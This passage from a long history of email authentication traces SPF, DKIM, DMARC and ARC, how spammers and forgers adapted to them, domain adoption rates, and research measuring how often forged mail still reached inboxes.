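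The two experiments also interfered with each other. Sender ID software could check the header address against existing SPF records, which domain owners had written for the envelope address. For example, an outside company might send the bakery's newsletter with its own address on the envelope and the bakery's in the From line. SPF checks the newsletter company's record, and the message passes. Sender ID checks the bakery's record, which doesn't list the company's server because SPF didn't need it there, and the message fails. Mehnle (2006) appealed on behalf of SPF's users and accused the IETF's leadership of ignoring the records that people had already published. The reply, reproduced in an IETF document on the appeal, warned participants that they might lose valid messages and suggested publishing a separate record for each system.

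The IETF asked operators to watch both experiments, SPF and Sender ID, for two years. SPF joined the standards track only in 2014, eleven years after Wong wrote it, and the IETF has since marked Sender ID as historic. DKIM's standardisation went more smoothly. Yahoo's DomainKeys merged with a similar design from Cisco, the IETF published a proposed standard in May 2007, and Hu and colleagues date its standardisation to 2011, seven years after the first draft. Operators didn't wait for these standards to be finished. *RepuScore* (Singaraju and Kang, 2007) reports that by 2007 senders were already authenticating about 35% of email by one method or another.

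### What spammers did with SPF

Bill Gates predicted in January 2004 that spam would be solved within two years. Wong's white paper included a timetable whose final entry reads "Spam ends. Bill Gates gets credit." Senders would publish SPF records by the end of 2004, forwarders would adapt by the middle of 2005, and that summer receivers would start rejecting mail that failed authentication. In the last quarter of 2005, providers would offer mailboxes that accepted only authenticated mail from reputable senders.

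Despite the joke at the end, the plan was serious, and it depended on more than authentication. Wong wrote that spammers would authenticate themselves too. Dmitri Alperovitch of the security company CipherTrust complained that many people believed SPF was designed to stop spam, when its purpose was to authenticate senders.

CipherTrust studied spammers' use of SPF by analysing about two million messages that its customers had received between May and August 2004, according to TechNewsWorld's *Survey Finds Spammers Embracing Sender Authentication*. CipherTrust's release, *Spammers Are Also Adopting SPF Standard* (2004), reported that 34% more spam than legitimate mail passed the SPF check, and that a spam message was three times more likely to pass than to fail.

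Some press coverage changed these figures. Route Fifty's *E-mail sender authentication* (2004) repeated the 34%, but Callaghan's *Spammers Skirt IP Authentication Attempts* (2004) gave it as 38%. TechNewsWorld wrote that spam was three times more likely to pass than legitimate mail, a different and much stronger claim.

If 134 spam messages passed for every 100 legitimate ones, about 57% of the mail that passed was spam. A pass was a sign of spam only if spam made up less than that share of the whole sample. If 70% of the sample was spam, for example, a message that passed was less likely to be spam than an average one. The comparison also reflects how few legitimate senders had started using authentication. Among the thousand largest American companies, the number using such protocols had risen from 11 to 31 since May.

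SPF's supporters disputed the conclusion. Bissex (2004) replied on a mailing list that SPF was never meant to identify good mail, and that a failed check was still an excellent sign of forgery. Bortzmeyer (2004), in a reply to Callaghan's article, doubted the whole study, partly because it mentioned Sender ID records before that standard was finished. Bortzmeyer also found few senders with SPF records in a personal collection of spam. So few receivers checked the records that spammers had little reason to publish them.

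MX Logic, another filtering company, found more spam with SPF records. It first put the share at 10%, according to Callaghan, and then at 16% in a sample of more than 400,000 spam messages from 29 August to 3 September 2004, as iTnews' *Spammers using new email authentication protocol* reported. The 16% could include messages that did not pass SPF, such as spam that forged the address of a large provider with an SPF record. The following June, MX Logic (2005) examined 17.7 million messages and found that 9% came from domains with SPF records, and that 84% of those domains sent spam. Both companies had a commercial interest in these findings because they sold filters that did more than check SPF, but later research confirmed that spammers used SPF.

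By 2011 an SPF pass had become a better sign that a message was legitimate. In the logs that Mori and colleagues studied, 39% of all messages were spam, but only 14% of those that passed SPF were. Still, 174,000 spam messages passed. A failure was weaker evidence of spam than Bissex had hoped, since 22% of the messages with an outright fail were legitimate, as were more than half of the softfails. The company's server had turned away many infected computers before the logs began, so spam would have made up a larger share of the failures in its unfiltered mail.

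Microsoft's *Think SPF is widely deployed* reports an even smaller difference in mail that had got past the company's IP filters. Of that mail, 90% was good overall, compared with 94% of messages that passed SPF and 87% of messages from domains with no SPF record. A receiver that rejected mail from domains with no record would have turned away a great many honest senders.

### Why a valid identity is cheap

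SPF and DKIM let a domain's owner specify which mail is genuine, but a spammer can own a domain. Scott Chasin of MX Logic told TechNewsWorld in 2004 that anyone could buy one for $5 and give it an SPF record. A spammer who sent a million messages from that domain would pay 0.0005 cents per message for it. A DKIM key costs nothing, because a program can generate one in moments.

Honest organisations often had more work to do than spammers. Wong advised them to begin by finding every source of their mail, including billing systems and staff who sent from elsewhere, because genuine messages would fail the check if they came from a server missing from the SPF record. A spammer with one new domain and one rented server had only that server to list. Spammers who controlled infected computers could publish a record that authorised every IP address on the internet, as Steve Linford of Spamhaus pointed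 out in 2004, and Mori and colleagues later found hundreds of spam domains with such records. Other spam domains authorised single machines, some of which belonged to reputable providers such as Google. The researchers suspected that spammers had added these to look respectable.

Wong's white paper includes a mock guide for spammers that forecasts how they would adapt. They could buy a domain and use it at once, before it had a reputation. If receivers learned to distrust new domains, spammers could leave one idle until it looked established, or buy a respected domain that had expired. They could also use an infected computer to send mail through its owner's real account to people in the owner's address book. Wong expected receivers to respond to each move, for instance by wiping a domain's reputation when it changed hands, and expected providers to limit how much each customer could send.

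Even a cheap identity is of some use to receivers, because a spammer who stops forging addresses has to send from a domain that receivers can recognize, and has to buy another to escape a bad record. A columnist in eWEEK argued that spammers who published SPF records were "playing right into our hands", but that was true only if someone kept track of which domains had sent spam.

### Reputation, and how Gmail scored senders

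The Messaging Anti-Abuse Working Group (MAAWG), an industry body, described a two-step process of authenticating whoever takes responsibility for a message and then consulting their reputation. Wong added accreditation for senders with no history, and roughly distinguished the two services by who pays. Senders pay to be on an accreditation list, while receivers pay for a reputation service's opinion.

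Under this plan, receivers would mainly list good domains. Singaraju and Kang observed that spammers' domains come and go. Honest organisations usually keep theirs, so a list of good domains needs less upkeep than a list of bad ones. It also makes a new $5 domain much less useful to a spammer, because receivers no longer assume that an unfamiliar name is honest.

*Sender Reputation in a Large Webmail Service* (Taylor, 2006), a conference paper by Google engineer Bradley Taylor, describes how Gmail scored domains that it had authenticated with SPF or DomainKeys. Many domains had published no records for either, so Gmail also used a "best guess" rule, under which a server could pass if, for example, its IP address was close to that of the domain's website or mail server. *Gmail's spam filtering* (Metro, 2007), a summary of the paper for a Linux users' group, reports that these methods together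 authenticated 74% of legitimate mail and about 40% of spam.

Gmail gave each domain a score from 0 to 100, roughly the percentage of its mail that was not spam. It calculated the score from its filter's past decisions and users' clicks on "Report Spam" and "Not Spam". As a simplified example, suppose a domain sends 10,000 messages, and the filter puts 9,600 in inboxes and 400 in spam folders. Users then report 100 of the inbox messages as spam and mark 50 of the messages in spam folders as not spam. That makes 9,550 good messages and a score of 95.5.

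The domain's score then determined where its next message went. Under the thresholds in Metro's summary, mail from a domain scoring below about 5 went to the spam folder, and mail from one scoring above about 80 went to the inbox. Only the mail in between needed a statistical filter. A user's own choices about a sender apparently overrode the general score.

Buchheit (2007), in *Email blackmail is unnecessary*, quotes Taylor's finding that the scores of spammers' domains clustered around zero and those of most other domains between 90 and 100. Many of the messages in the middle came from legitimate bulk senders with poor practices. eBay scored 98.2, high enough for its mail to skip the filter. Five large American internet providers planned to charge businesses for guaranteed delivery, and Buchheit, who had created Gmail, used the result to argue that senders could earn good delivery through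 their behaviour instead.

Taylor took the cluster at zero as confirmation that those domains were spammers, since users who disagreed would have unmarked the mail and raised the scores. That assumes users check their spam folders, but Taylor and two other Google engineers, Fingal and Aberdeen, later admitted in *The War Against Spam* that many hardly ever do, and that people who download their mail to another program may never vote at all. If the filter misjudged a small honest sender early on, its decisions would lower the sender's score, and the low score would send later messages to a folder that few people checked. Metro noticed that Taylor's paper didn't explain what Gmail did with senders it could not authenticate, who accounted for a quarter of the good mail and 60% of the spam.

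Google kept the scores to itself. Taylor hoped that a third party would offer similar scores to everyone. A developer of SpamAssassin, the free filter, told Buchheit that the project would gladly use such data, but that the old DNS blocklists were still the only public source. A mail service may not have needed to be large to use reputation this way. In *A Zero Spam Mail System* (2019), a mailing-list discussion, the operator of a service for a few friends and relatives recalled that a list of reputable domains had let 90% of their legitimate mail skip the content filter. That was an easy case, though, because the few users had similar correspondents. In the same discussion, Brandon Long of Google said that Gmail's system had become faster and tracked many more features, but that Taylor would still recognise it.

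Singaraju and Kang designed RepuScore, a shared system in which organisations would send their scores to a central authority. With any such score, responding faster when a domain turns bad also lets a patient spammer build a good reputation sooner. RepuScore's formula illustrates this. At the end of each period, the new score is α times the old one plus (1 − α) times the share of good mail in that period, with α between 0 and 1. Suppose a domain with a score of 0.95 starts to send nothing but spam. If α is 0.9, its score takes seven periods to fall below 0.5, and a new domain that starts at 0.5 needs nine periods of sending only good mail to rise above 0.8. If α is 0.5, the fall takes one period and the rise takes two. RepuScore also had to guard against false votes, since a spammer could pose as several receivers and praise its own mail. It gave more weight to reports from reputable organisations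 and ignored those from organisations with low scores.

Taylor and colleagues at Gmail reported that, as more receivers used SPF and DKIM, spammers got around the scores by opening accounts at reputable free mail services. They used programs to create thousands of accounts and got people to solve the CAPTCHAs, sometimes for pay and sometimes without knowing what the puzzles were for. Mail from these accounts passed authentication and benefited from the provider's good reputation. The provider had to catch the spam before it went out, which was harder than filtering incoming mail because the provider often didn't learn whether the recipient had treated a message as spam.

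## DMARC and the reasons domains held back, 2012 to 2023

By 2011 a receiver could use SPF or DKIM to learn which domain had authorised a message, but that domain did not have to match the one in the From address. Receivers also had to guess what to do when a check failed, because forwarding can make genuine mail fail. Ana could end her SPF record with "-all", but receivers often ignored it, and they didn't tell her what they had done with her mail.

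Some large companies solved this privately. A sender and a receiver would agree that the receiver should refuse unauthenticated mail in the sender's name and report what it had seen. *Domain-based Message Authentication, Reporting, and Conformance (DMARC)* (Kucherawy and Zwicky, 2015) describes these arrangements as generally successful, but every pair of companies had to negotiate its own. A group that included Google, Microsoft, PayPal and Yahoo turned the practice into a public specification, DMARC, and released it in January 2012. The 2015 document was informational only, and DMARC stayed off the IETF's standards track until May 2026, when Herr and Levine (2026) published a revised version, *Domain-Based Message Authentication, Reporting, and Conformance (DMARC)*.

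### When SPF passes and DMARC fails

In addition to the existing checks, DMARC requires the domain in the From address to match a domain that SPF or DKIM has verified. This match is called alignment, and one aligned pass is enough. Ana's message to Ben still passes DMARC after forwarding because, although SPF fails at mailbox.example, her DKIM signature still passes and carries the bakery's domain.

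Now suppose a forger owns crook.example and has published an SPF record for it that lists the machine at 192.0.2.99. The forger writes to Ben from that machine, with billing@crook.example on the envelope and ana@bakery.example in the From line. The school's server works through the message as follows:

1. It takes crook.example from the envelope, fetches that domain's SPF record and finds 192.0.2.99 in it. SPF passes.
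2. It finds a DKIM signature with *d=crook.example* and checks it against the key that the forger has published. DKIM passes too.
3. It takes bakery.example from the From line and compares it with the verified domain, crook.example. They differ, so DMARC fails.
4. It looks up the DNS entry _dmarc.bakery.example to see what Ana wants done with such mail.

Kucherawy and Zwicky chose the From address because every valid message has one and most mail programs display it. They considered the Sender line, which Sender ID had used, but rejected it because readers may never see it, an objection Sender ID's critics had also raised.

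Legitimate mail can fail DMARC just as forged mail does. The firm that sends the bakery's newsletter puts its own address on the envelope, signs with its own key and writes the bakery's address in the From line. SPF and DKIM pass for the firm's domain, but DMARC fails because that domain doesn't match the one in the From line. Ana can fix this by publishing a DKIM key for the firm under bakery.example, or by letting the firm use an envelope address at news.bakery.example.

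The second fix works because alignment is "relaxed" by default, so two names match if they belong to the same registered domain. In "strict" mode they must be identical. Relaxed mode saves work, but an outsider who gains control of the SPF record for news.bakery.example can send mail as ana@bakery.example and pass DMARC.

### Three policies and a daily report

Ana's first DMARC record might look like this:

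```
v=DMARC1; p=none; rua=mailto:reports@bakery.example
```

The *p* field of a DMARC record holds the domain owner's policy. With "none", the owner asks receivers to treat mail as they would without the record, so the record gives the domain no protection. With "quarantine", the owner asks them to treat failing messages as suspicious, which usually means sending them to the spam folder. With "reject", the owner asks them to refuse those messages. Only "quarantine" and "reject" count as enforcement.

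A domain's DMARC policy is a request to mail receivers. According to Kucherawy and Zwicky, a receiver should try to follow it but may accept a failing message if it has a reason to, and should then tell the domain's owner. A receiver may also refuse a message that passes, since a spammer can publish a DMARC record as easily as anyone else.

The *rua* field gives an address for reports. Each participating receiver sends a daily file listing the machines that have sent mail in the bakery's name, with the number of messages, the SPF and DKIM results, whether they aligned, and what the receiver did with the mail. Before DMARC, domain owners could not regularly get this information without a private arrangement. Kucherawy and Zwicky expected owners to be more willing to enforce a policy if they could see its effect.

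Suppose a week of reports shows that all 1,000 messages from Ana's provider pass. The failures are 200 messages from the newsletter firm, 25 copies of her posts to the bakers' mailing list, and 400 messages from machines she has never heard of. If she had published "reject", receivers that followed it would have refused 400 forgeries and 225 genuine messages. Once the newsletter firm signs with her key, the number of genuine messages refused would fall to 25. She can't fix those by herself, because someone else runs the list.

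The reports don't label the forgeries, so Ana has to recognise which machines send mail for her. This is quick for a bakery but slow for a university whose departments buy their own mailing services. A domain owner could phase in a stricter policy by adding a percentage. With "reject" and *pct=20*, receivers would refuse about 85 of the 425 messages that still fail and treat the other 340 as if the policy were "quarantine".

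If a domain's SPF record ends in "-all", some receivers reject a message as soon as it fails SPF, before they have read it and its DKIM signature. These receivers refuse Ana's forwarded mail even though it would have passed DMARC.

### Yahoo and the mailing lists, April 2014

DMARC's designers intended it mainly for what they called transactional mail, such as receipts and bank notices, which a company sends directly to its customers from machines it knows. People use personal addresses less predictably, posting to mailing lists and sending from services their provider doesn't know about.

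In the spring of 2014, criminals sent millions of people phishing messages that appeared to come from acquaintances with Yahoo accounts. The messages were very effective because the criminals had secretly collected data on who knew whom, according to *Yahoo to expand use of strict DMARC policy* (2015), a post on the DMARC group's website. The messages did not come from Yahoo's servers and had no valid Yahoo signature, as Virus Bulletin's *Yahoo's DMARC policy wreaks havoc among mailing lists* (2014) explains, so a strict policy would catch them. On 4 April, Yahoo changed its DMARC policy for yahoo.com from "none" to "reject".

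Over the following days, mailing lists around the world began to fail. A post to a list usually loses its DKIM signature and passes SPF only for the list's own domain, so posts from Yahoo users failed DMARC, and every receiver that followed Yahoo's policy rejected them. John Levine, who had written the technical description of blocklists, stressed in *Yahoo addresses a security problem by breaking every mailing list* (CircleID, 2014) that the lists were doing nothing wrong.

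Mailing list subscribers who had never used Yahoo were affected too. If Gmail refused a Yahoo user's post, the list's software counted the refusal against the Gmail subscriber. After several refusals, the software typically treats the subscriber's mailbox as dead and suspends the subscription. In *Yahoo DMARC breakage*, a discussion among network operators, Simes (2014) confirmed the problem on several lists and responded by holding every post from a Yahoo address for a moderator to review.

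Yahoo estimated that the change affected about 30,000 services that send email, and called the fix they needed "important and not terribly difficult to implement". Miles Fidelman, who supported some of the lists, quoted this to other operators and compared the policy to a denial-of-service attack. Laszlo (2014) replied that Yahoo didn't want such messages and had made that clear. That is a fair defense of refusals by Yahoo's own servers, but Yahoo had also asked all other providers to refuse the messages, including providers whose users had chosen to join the lists.

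Crocker (2014), a co-author of the DKIM standard, called the damage "an informed corporate choice" and thought Yahoo had understood the effects in advance, since it had helped develop DMARC. In a message that Popovitch (2014) quoted, Elizabeth Zwicky, the Yahoo engineer who co-edited the specification, acknowledged that "significant use cases are broken". In October 2015 Yahoo announced that it would extend the strict policy to more of its domains, so it evidently considered the damage acceptable.

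Much of that burden fell on the list operators. Herrin (2014) described the workaround, in which the list replaces the author's address in the From line with its own, so that a post from Levine appears as "John Levine" followed by the list's address. The From domain then matches the envelope domain, and the message passes DMARC. Readers no longer see the author's real address, and private replies depend on a separate Reply-To line. The workaround also gets people used to seeing a familiar name beside an unfamiliar address, as in many phishing messages.

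Yahoo could impose these changes because every large list needed to keep its Yahoo subscribers. If Ana had published "reject" for the bakery, no list would have changed its software for her, and her posts would have disappeared.

### ARC, a repair that depends on trust

Engineers then designed Authenticated Received Chain (ARC), which lets a mailing list pass on a message's authentication results from before the list changed it. The IETF published ARC as an experimental protocol in 2019.

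When Ana posts to the bakers' list, the list's server checks her message on arrival and records the result in a new header, for example that DKIM passed for bakery.example. It then adds the footer, signs the altered message, and adds another signature, called a seal, which covers the recorded result and any earlier ARC entries. If a subscriber's school forwards the message, the school's server can add its own numbered set of ARC entries. The last receiver finds that DMARC fails, checks the seals, sees that the message passed when it reached the list, and may deliver it.

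A valid seal shows which server recorded the result, but not that the result is true. A spammer could write a message in Ana's name, falsely record that it had passed DKIM for bakery.example, and seal that record with a valid key. The receiver therefore has to know which lists and forwarders to trust. Gmail can learn this from the large volume of mail it handles, but a small receiver may see too little mail from most lists to judge them.

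ARC also has an adoption problem, since it helps only if both the list and the receiver use it. A list whose subscribers are spread over hundreds of receivers can't count on all of them to use ARC, so it still has to rewrite the From address. Hu and colleagues, writing while ARC was in development, pointed out that it would add another protocol to the ones administrators were already slow to adopt.

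### How many domains published records

Receivers adopted DMARC quickly. By April 2014 it protected 85% of mailboxes in the United States and 60% worldwide, according to Bird's *Yahoo's bold move changing DMARC policy from report to reject*, a blog post from an email company. A handful of providers hold most of the world's mailboxes, so only a few had to adopt DMARC to reach that coverage, but publishing a DMARC record was up to the owners of hundreds of millions of domains.

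Durumeric and colleagues measured adoption among the million most popular domains in 2015, as did Foster and colleagues. Hu and Wang cited both sets of results in *Revisiting Email Spoofing Attacks* (2018) and repeated the measurement in January and October 2017. Bayer, Nosyk and colleagues collected a much larger sample of 251 million domains in the second quarter of 2021 and obtained results for about 247 million, which they reported in *Study on Domain Name System (DNS) Abuse Technical Report* (2022).

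| Date | Sample | SPF | DMARC | Enforcement (quarantine or reject) |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2015 | Top million domains, two studies cited by Hu and Wang | 40% | about 1% | not given |
| January 2017 | Top million domains, Hu and Wang | 47.7% | 3.1% | 0.7% (reject 0.4%) |
| October 2017 | Top million domains, Hu and Wang | 49.3% | 4.6% | 1.0% (reject 0.6%) |
| Second quarter of 2021 | About 247 million domains of all kinds, Bayer and colleagues | 31.4% | 3.3% | 1.6% (reject 1.2%) |

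The enforcement percentages are shares of all domains in the sample. They all predate 2024, when large mail providers began requiring DMARC from bulk senders and adoption rose faster.

SPF grew more slowly between 2015 and 2017 than it appears in the table, because the 2017 figures include records with errors. Hu and Wang compare the 40% from 2015 with the share of domains that had valid records, which was 43.4% in January 2017 and 45.0% in October. DMARC grew by about half in those nine months, but around 80% of the net increase in valid records came from domains with a policy of "none". Some very large sites also published "none", including Apple, eBay and the *New York Times*, while PayPal, LinkedIn and Netflix published "reject".

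The 49% figure for SPF comes from popular domains and the 31% figure from a sample of all registered domains, so the drop does not mean that domains gave it up. Popular domains usually belong to organisations that send mail, employ technical staff and have a name worth forging. The wider sample also includes millions of domains that hold a forgotten project or nothing. Even among popular domains, Hu and Wang's data for October 2017 show that 59.2% of those with a mail server published an SPF record, while the share works out at 9% for the roughly 196,000 without one.

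Among domains that use DMARC, 48% enforced it in the 2021 sample, compared with 22% in October 2017. Owners may have become more confident, but the different samples could also explain the increase. The owner of a domain that never sends mail can publish "reject" without risking the loss of genuine messages, and a sample of all domains contains many more such domains.

A record may also be broken. Of the 77 million SPF records that Bayer and colleagues tested, 3.2 million produced a permanent error, and about half of those required too many DNS lookups. SPF allows a receiver ten lookups per message. Each "include" in Ana's record uses at least one, and the included record may require more, so a business that adds a newsletter firm, a booking service and an accounting program can exceed the limit without noticing. Almost 700,000 domains had published two or more SPF records, which also causes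 an error.

The table leaves out DKIM because a scan of domains can't count it reliably. A researcher can look up an SPF or DMARC record with only the domain's name, but finding a DKIM key also requires the key's name, such as "june", which appears only in the headers of signed messages. Researchers could guess common names but would miss the rest. Mail providers can count signatures in the mail they receive, but that gives the share of messages that are signed, not the share of domains that sign.

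### Why adoption can stall

Six years before DMARC appeared, *Bootstrapping the Adoption of Internet Security Protocols* (Ozment and Schechter, 2006) modeled why protections like it spread slowly. Each user *i* has a fixed cost of adopting, *cᵢ*. The benefit, *bᵢ(A)*, depends on *A*, the set of users who have adopted, and never falls when more join. A user adopts once *bᵢ(A)* is greater than *cᵢ*.

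In a simple example with ten mail providers, adoption costs each provider 3 and brings it a benefit of 1 for every other provider that has adopted. If all ten adopted, each would receive 9 for a cost of 3. But the first to adopt would receive nothing for that cost, so nobody starts. If three had already adopted, a fourth would only break even. The critical mass is four, because a fifth provider would then gain 4 for a cost of 3, and the rest would follow.

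Adoption can also stall partway. Suppose two of the ten are banks, and each gains an extra 4 from adopting because criminals can no longer forge its name. Both adopt regardless of what the others do. The other eight would each gain 2 at a cost of 3, so they stay out, and adoption stops at 20%. If somebody paid or forced two more to join, the remaining six would follow on their own.

The share of users needed for critical mass depends on how the benefit grows as more users adopt. Ozment and Schechter preferred a curve on which early adopters add more benefit than later ones, *B(x) = ln(1 + Qx)*, where *x* is the share of users who have adopted, *Q = eᴹ − 1*, and *M* is the benefit at full adoption. If *M* is 4 and the cost is 3, adoption becomes worthwhile at about 36%. If the benefit instead rises in a straight line to 4, the threshold is 75%. Without a measurement of the real curve for email,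 the model can explain why adoption stalls but can't predict the percentage at which it will take off.

Authentication also brings receivers little benefit until most senders have adopted it. Ozment and Schechter illustrate this with a receiver, Bob, who gets an unsigned message that appears to come from Alice. If Alice signs all her mail, the message is a forgery. If she has never adopted signatures, Bob can't tell whether it is genuine. Suppose he receives 100 genuine messages and 10 forgeries. If 20 of the genuine messages are signed, refusing all unsigned mail stops the 10 forgeries but also blocks 80 genuine messages. If 95 are signed, it blocks only 5. Bob is therefore better off accepting everything until most senders sign their mail.

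Ozment and Schechter's solution was for each adopter to publish a statement in a secured version of DNS. Receivers could then refuse unsigned mail from domains that had published the statement while still accepting it from others. A DMARC policy of "reject" is a statement of this kind, although most owners publish it in ordinary DNS. DMARC should have removed the obstacle for receivers, and their rapid adoption of it suggests that it largely did.

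But it left domain owners with a different risk, that receivers would refuse their genuine mail. This happens to Ana if she forgets to include the newsletter firm in her statement. A lack of critical mass also explains DMARC's slow adoption less well than it explained SPF's in 2004, when few receivers checked the records. By 2014 most large receivers checked DMARC, so a bank that published "reject" got much of the benefit at once, whatever other domains did. A bakery whose mail nobody forges gained almost nothing, and would have gained little more if every other bakery had joined.

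Hu and colleagues adapted the model and reached a similar conclusion about domains that have a website but no mail service. For these domains, they draw the cost and benefit of adoption as flat lines, meaning that neither changes as others adopt. If the benefit is below the cost, no critical mass of adopters can raise it above.

Adoption of HTTPS, the secure form of web connection, stalled in a similar way in the years up to 2006. Visa and Mastercard required online merchants to use it, and merchants did, but Ozment and Schechter counted fewer than 300,000 certificates when .com alone had 40 million names. By contrast, SSH, a secure way to control a computer remotely, spread easily because an organisation that switched its own machines got nearly the whole benefit without waiting for anyone else.

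### What nine administrators reported

Hu and colleagues asked administrators why they had or hadn't adopted the three standards. They wrote to the administrators of 4,000 popular domains, and nine agreed to take part. Two gave interviews in person, and seven answered the same open questions in writing.

One university administrator said "I am not motivated to set up SPF", because publishing records mainly helps other providers protect their users. The same administrator wanted everyone who wrote to the university to have set it up. The participants' own systems showed the same pattern. Of the eight mail services the researchers could test, seven checked incoming mail with all three standards, but only three had published both SPF and DMARC records.

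Both interviewees said that leaving the records out also generally carries no penalty from receivers unless something else about the mail looks suspicious. One of them, who ran a department's mail, saw too few others adopting to make the work worthwhile. The providers in the model don't start for the same reason.

Domain owners kept their policies weak because they feared losing real mail. A participant from an advertising service suggested that owners worry they have forgotten something and that their own mistake will get their mail refused. Another, from a second university, said that enforcement would require finding every legitimate source of mail, including marketing tools that departments had bought without telling central IT, and then preventing more unreported purchases. The participant said many administrators don't have time for that.

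Receivers also had a reason to be lenient. If a partner's SPF record is wrong, it can be easier to fetch the message from the spam folder than to persuade the partner to correct the record and resend the message. But if the receiver just fetches the message, the partner never learns about the mistake.

Several obstacles were more mundane. Three participants said that coordinating with whoever ran their DNS was extra work. Organisations that rented their mail service depended on the supplier to support the standards. One participant complained that DKIM signatures break when a server rewraps long lines, which made both DKIM and DMARC less attractive. The participant from a payment company thought that DMARC was easier to deploy than people believed, and that its reputation for difficulty was the obstacle. This participant and one other said that banks and popular services have a stronger reason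 to adopt because criminals forge their names.

The study received nine replies to 4,000 requests, a response rate of about 0.2%. A sample this small can show that a reason exists and how it works, but not how common it is. A random sample of nine would have a 96% chance of including at least one administrator with a reason shared by 30% of all administrators, and a 61% chance for a reason shared by 10%. But these nine were volunteers, and three worked at universities, two of them at the same one. Administrators who had never heard of DMARC probably had little wish to discuss it with researchers, so the study likely understates how often domains held back because their administrators didn't know about it.

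The large share of DMARC records with a policy of "none" is what one would expect if owners feared losing mail, and Yahoo's experience showed that the fear was reasonable. There is also some evidence of inattention. Bayer and colleagues describe an earlier study in which researchers had national computer emergency teams warn the owners of prominent domains, including those of banks, about faulty SPF and DMARC settings. After a single warning, the owners of 23.2% of the domains changed their settings. For those owners, the change can't have been very difficult or risky. The study doesn't show how many of the others decided the risk was too great and how many never read the warning.

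## What authenticated mail still let through, 2018 to 2026

A domain owner who publishes a "reject" policy still depends on each receiver to check and enforce it. Hu and Wang, who had found that few domains published such a policy, also tested receivers by sending them forged mail.

### Forged mail at 35 providers

The researchers opened accounts at 35 popular mail providers and sent messages to them from forged addresses. After a small trial in August 2017, they ran the main test in December 2017 and January 2018, sending 1,500 messages to each provider. The forged addresses used 30 well-known domains. Ten had no SPF, DKIM or DMARC records, ten had records with a DMARC policy of "none", and ten had a policy of "reject". Most of the messages were blank or harmless, so a spam filter had little reason to block them apart from the forged address.

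Every provider except Hotmail delivered at least one forgery to the inbox. Sixteen of the 35 checked all three standards, and their results varied greatly with the policy of the imitated domain:

| Imitated domain | Forgeries reaching the inbox, average of 16 providers | At Gmail |
|---|---|---|
| No records | 60% | 93% |
| DMARC policy of "none" | 45% | 66% |
| DMARC policy of "reject" | 13% | 0% |

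In *Re-examining Email Spoofing in the Context of Spear Phishing*, Wang also gives the 13% as the share of forgeries that got through when both the domain owner and the email provider were strict. But ten of the sixteen providers, including Gmail and Yahoo, let in no forgeries of domains with a "reject" policy. The other six looked up the owner's policy but treated it as advice, which the DMARC specification permits, and delivered between 7% and 64% of the forgeries.

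Another fifteen providers checked SPF or DKIM but not DMARC, and they delivered about 28% of the emails that forged domains with a "reject" policy. Over the whole test, they delivered 39% of forgeries, the same share as the sixteen providers that checked everything, because a DMARC check adds little when the domain owner has requested no action. The four providers that checked nothing delivered 94%.

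A provider that delivers a doubtful message can still warn the reader, but only six of the 35 did so on their websites, and only four of the 28 with phone apps did so in the apps. When the forged address belonged to one of the recipient's contacts, 25 providers made the forgery more convincing, for example by showing the contact's photo or earlier messages.

Hu and Wang also tested whether a warning helps. They sent a harmless imitation phishing message to people who had recently answered a survey for them. Of those who opened it, 49% clicked the link without a warning and 37% with one. Only 180 people opened the message, so the difference could be due to chance.

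### Programs that read one message differently

Chen, Paxson and Jiang (2020), in *Composition Kills*, found 18 types of attack that could get forged mail through even when the imitated domain had set up all three standards correctly and the receiver refused everything that failed DMARC. Together, those measures should block every forgery. The researchers tried the attacks on 10 mail providers and 19 mail programs, including the providers' own websites.

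The attacks work because several programs handle a message before Ben sees it. One checks SPF, another checks DKIM, a third compares the results with the From address, and Ben's mail program decides which name to display. Different developers wrote these programs, which can interpret a deliberately confusing message in different ways. Each program may then work correctly while Ben sees an address that none of them verified.

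At six of the ten providers, programs inside the mail server could interpret the same message differently. For example, the SPF program might verify one name while the DMARC program applied the result to another. At all ten, the server could check one address while the reader's mail program displayed a different one. All ten were also vulnerable to altered copies of genuine mail. A DKIM signature covers only the header lines that the signer chose, and sometimes only part of the text, so an attacker who has received a signed message can add material that the signature doesn't cover and send it on.

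Many of these weaknesses exist because mail programs deliberately accept badly formed messages, since refusing them would lose legitimate mail. Mail.ru told the researchers that it could not yet block messages with ambiguous addresses because too many genuine messages had unusual headers. The DKIM standard describes a way of signing that prevents additions to the header, but Yahoo was the only one of the ten to use it. Mail.ru had switched it off because of compatibility problems.

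Gmail fixed two of the attacks immediately. Microsoft disregarded the report because the attacks rely on deceiving the reader, which it didn't count as a security flaw. Yahoo mistook the attacks for errors in DNS settings. *Weak Links in Authentication Chains*, by Shen, Wang and colleagues, later reported further weaknesses, and 11 providers responded positively, this time including Yahoo.

Chen and colleagues suggested that the mail server pass the address it has verified directly to the mail program, so that the program doesn't have to interpret the message again. Their experiments show what a skilled attacker could do, but not how often criminals did it.

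### Forgeries that arrive through a forwarder

Forwarding makes genuine mail fail authentication, and the allowances receivers made for this gave forgers another weakness to exploit. In *Forward Pass*, Liu, Akiwate and colleagues (2023) studied 16 mail providers and four mailing-list services. They sent genuine and forged messages through every combination of forwarder and receiver, using test domains with each of the three DMARC policies. They counted an attack as successful only if the forgery reached the inbox without a warning.

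One weakness comes from sharing servers. Suppose mailhost.example handles mail for the bakery and for thousands of other businesses, all of which list its servers in their SPF records. Mailhost.example doesn't let one customer send new mail from another's address. But a customer's mailbox may forward messages from outside, and those can have any From address. A forgery in Ana's name can therefore leave from a server listed in her SPF record. All 16 providers shared servers among their customers, and 15 used the same servers for ordinary and forwarded mail.

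Ten of the 16 providers also let customers forward mail to any address without asking its owner. Weaknesses of this kind at six providers made it possible to forge mail from tens of thousands of popular domains, including those of the US State Department and most other cabinet departments.

Some receivers were also too trusting. Gmail, Outlook and Mail.ru relaxed their checks for mail that came through certain large providers, assuming those providers had already removed forgeries. Every provider also let its users accept mail from chosen domains even if it failed DMARC, though most set limits on this. This puts the user at risk, and if the mailbox forwards its mail, a forgery can also reach somebody else.

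Liu and colleagues point out that unrestricted forwarding harms receivers further along but not the provider that allows it. Open relays had created the same problem twenty years earlier, and other sites solved it by using blocklists to refuse the relays' mail. Receivers can't put similar pressure on Outlook because they would lose too much legitimate mail.

### SPF records that approve too many machines

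Czybik and colleagues scanned 12.8 million domains over five months in 2023 and found that 56.5% published an SPF record. About 2.9% of those records, or 211,018, contained errors that could stop them from working. Some were typing mistakes, such as "ipv4" where the standard requires "ip4". Others came from bad advice. The hosting company Bluehost recommended a record that needed 14 DNS lookups, four more than SPF allows.

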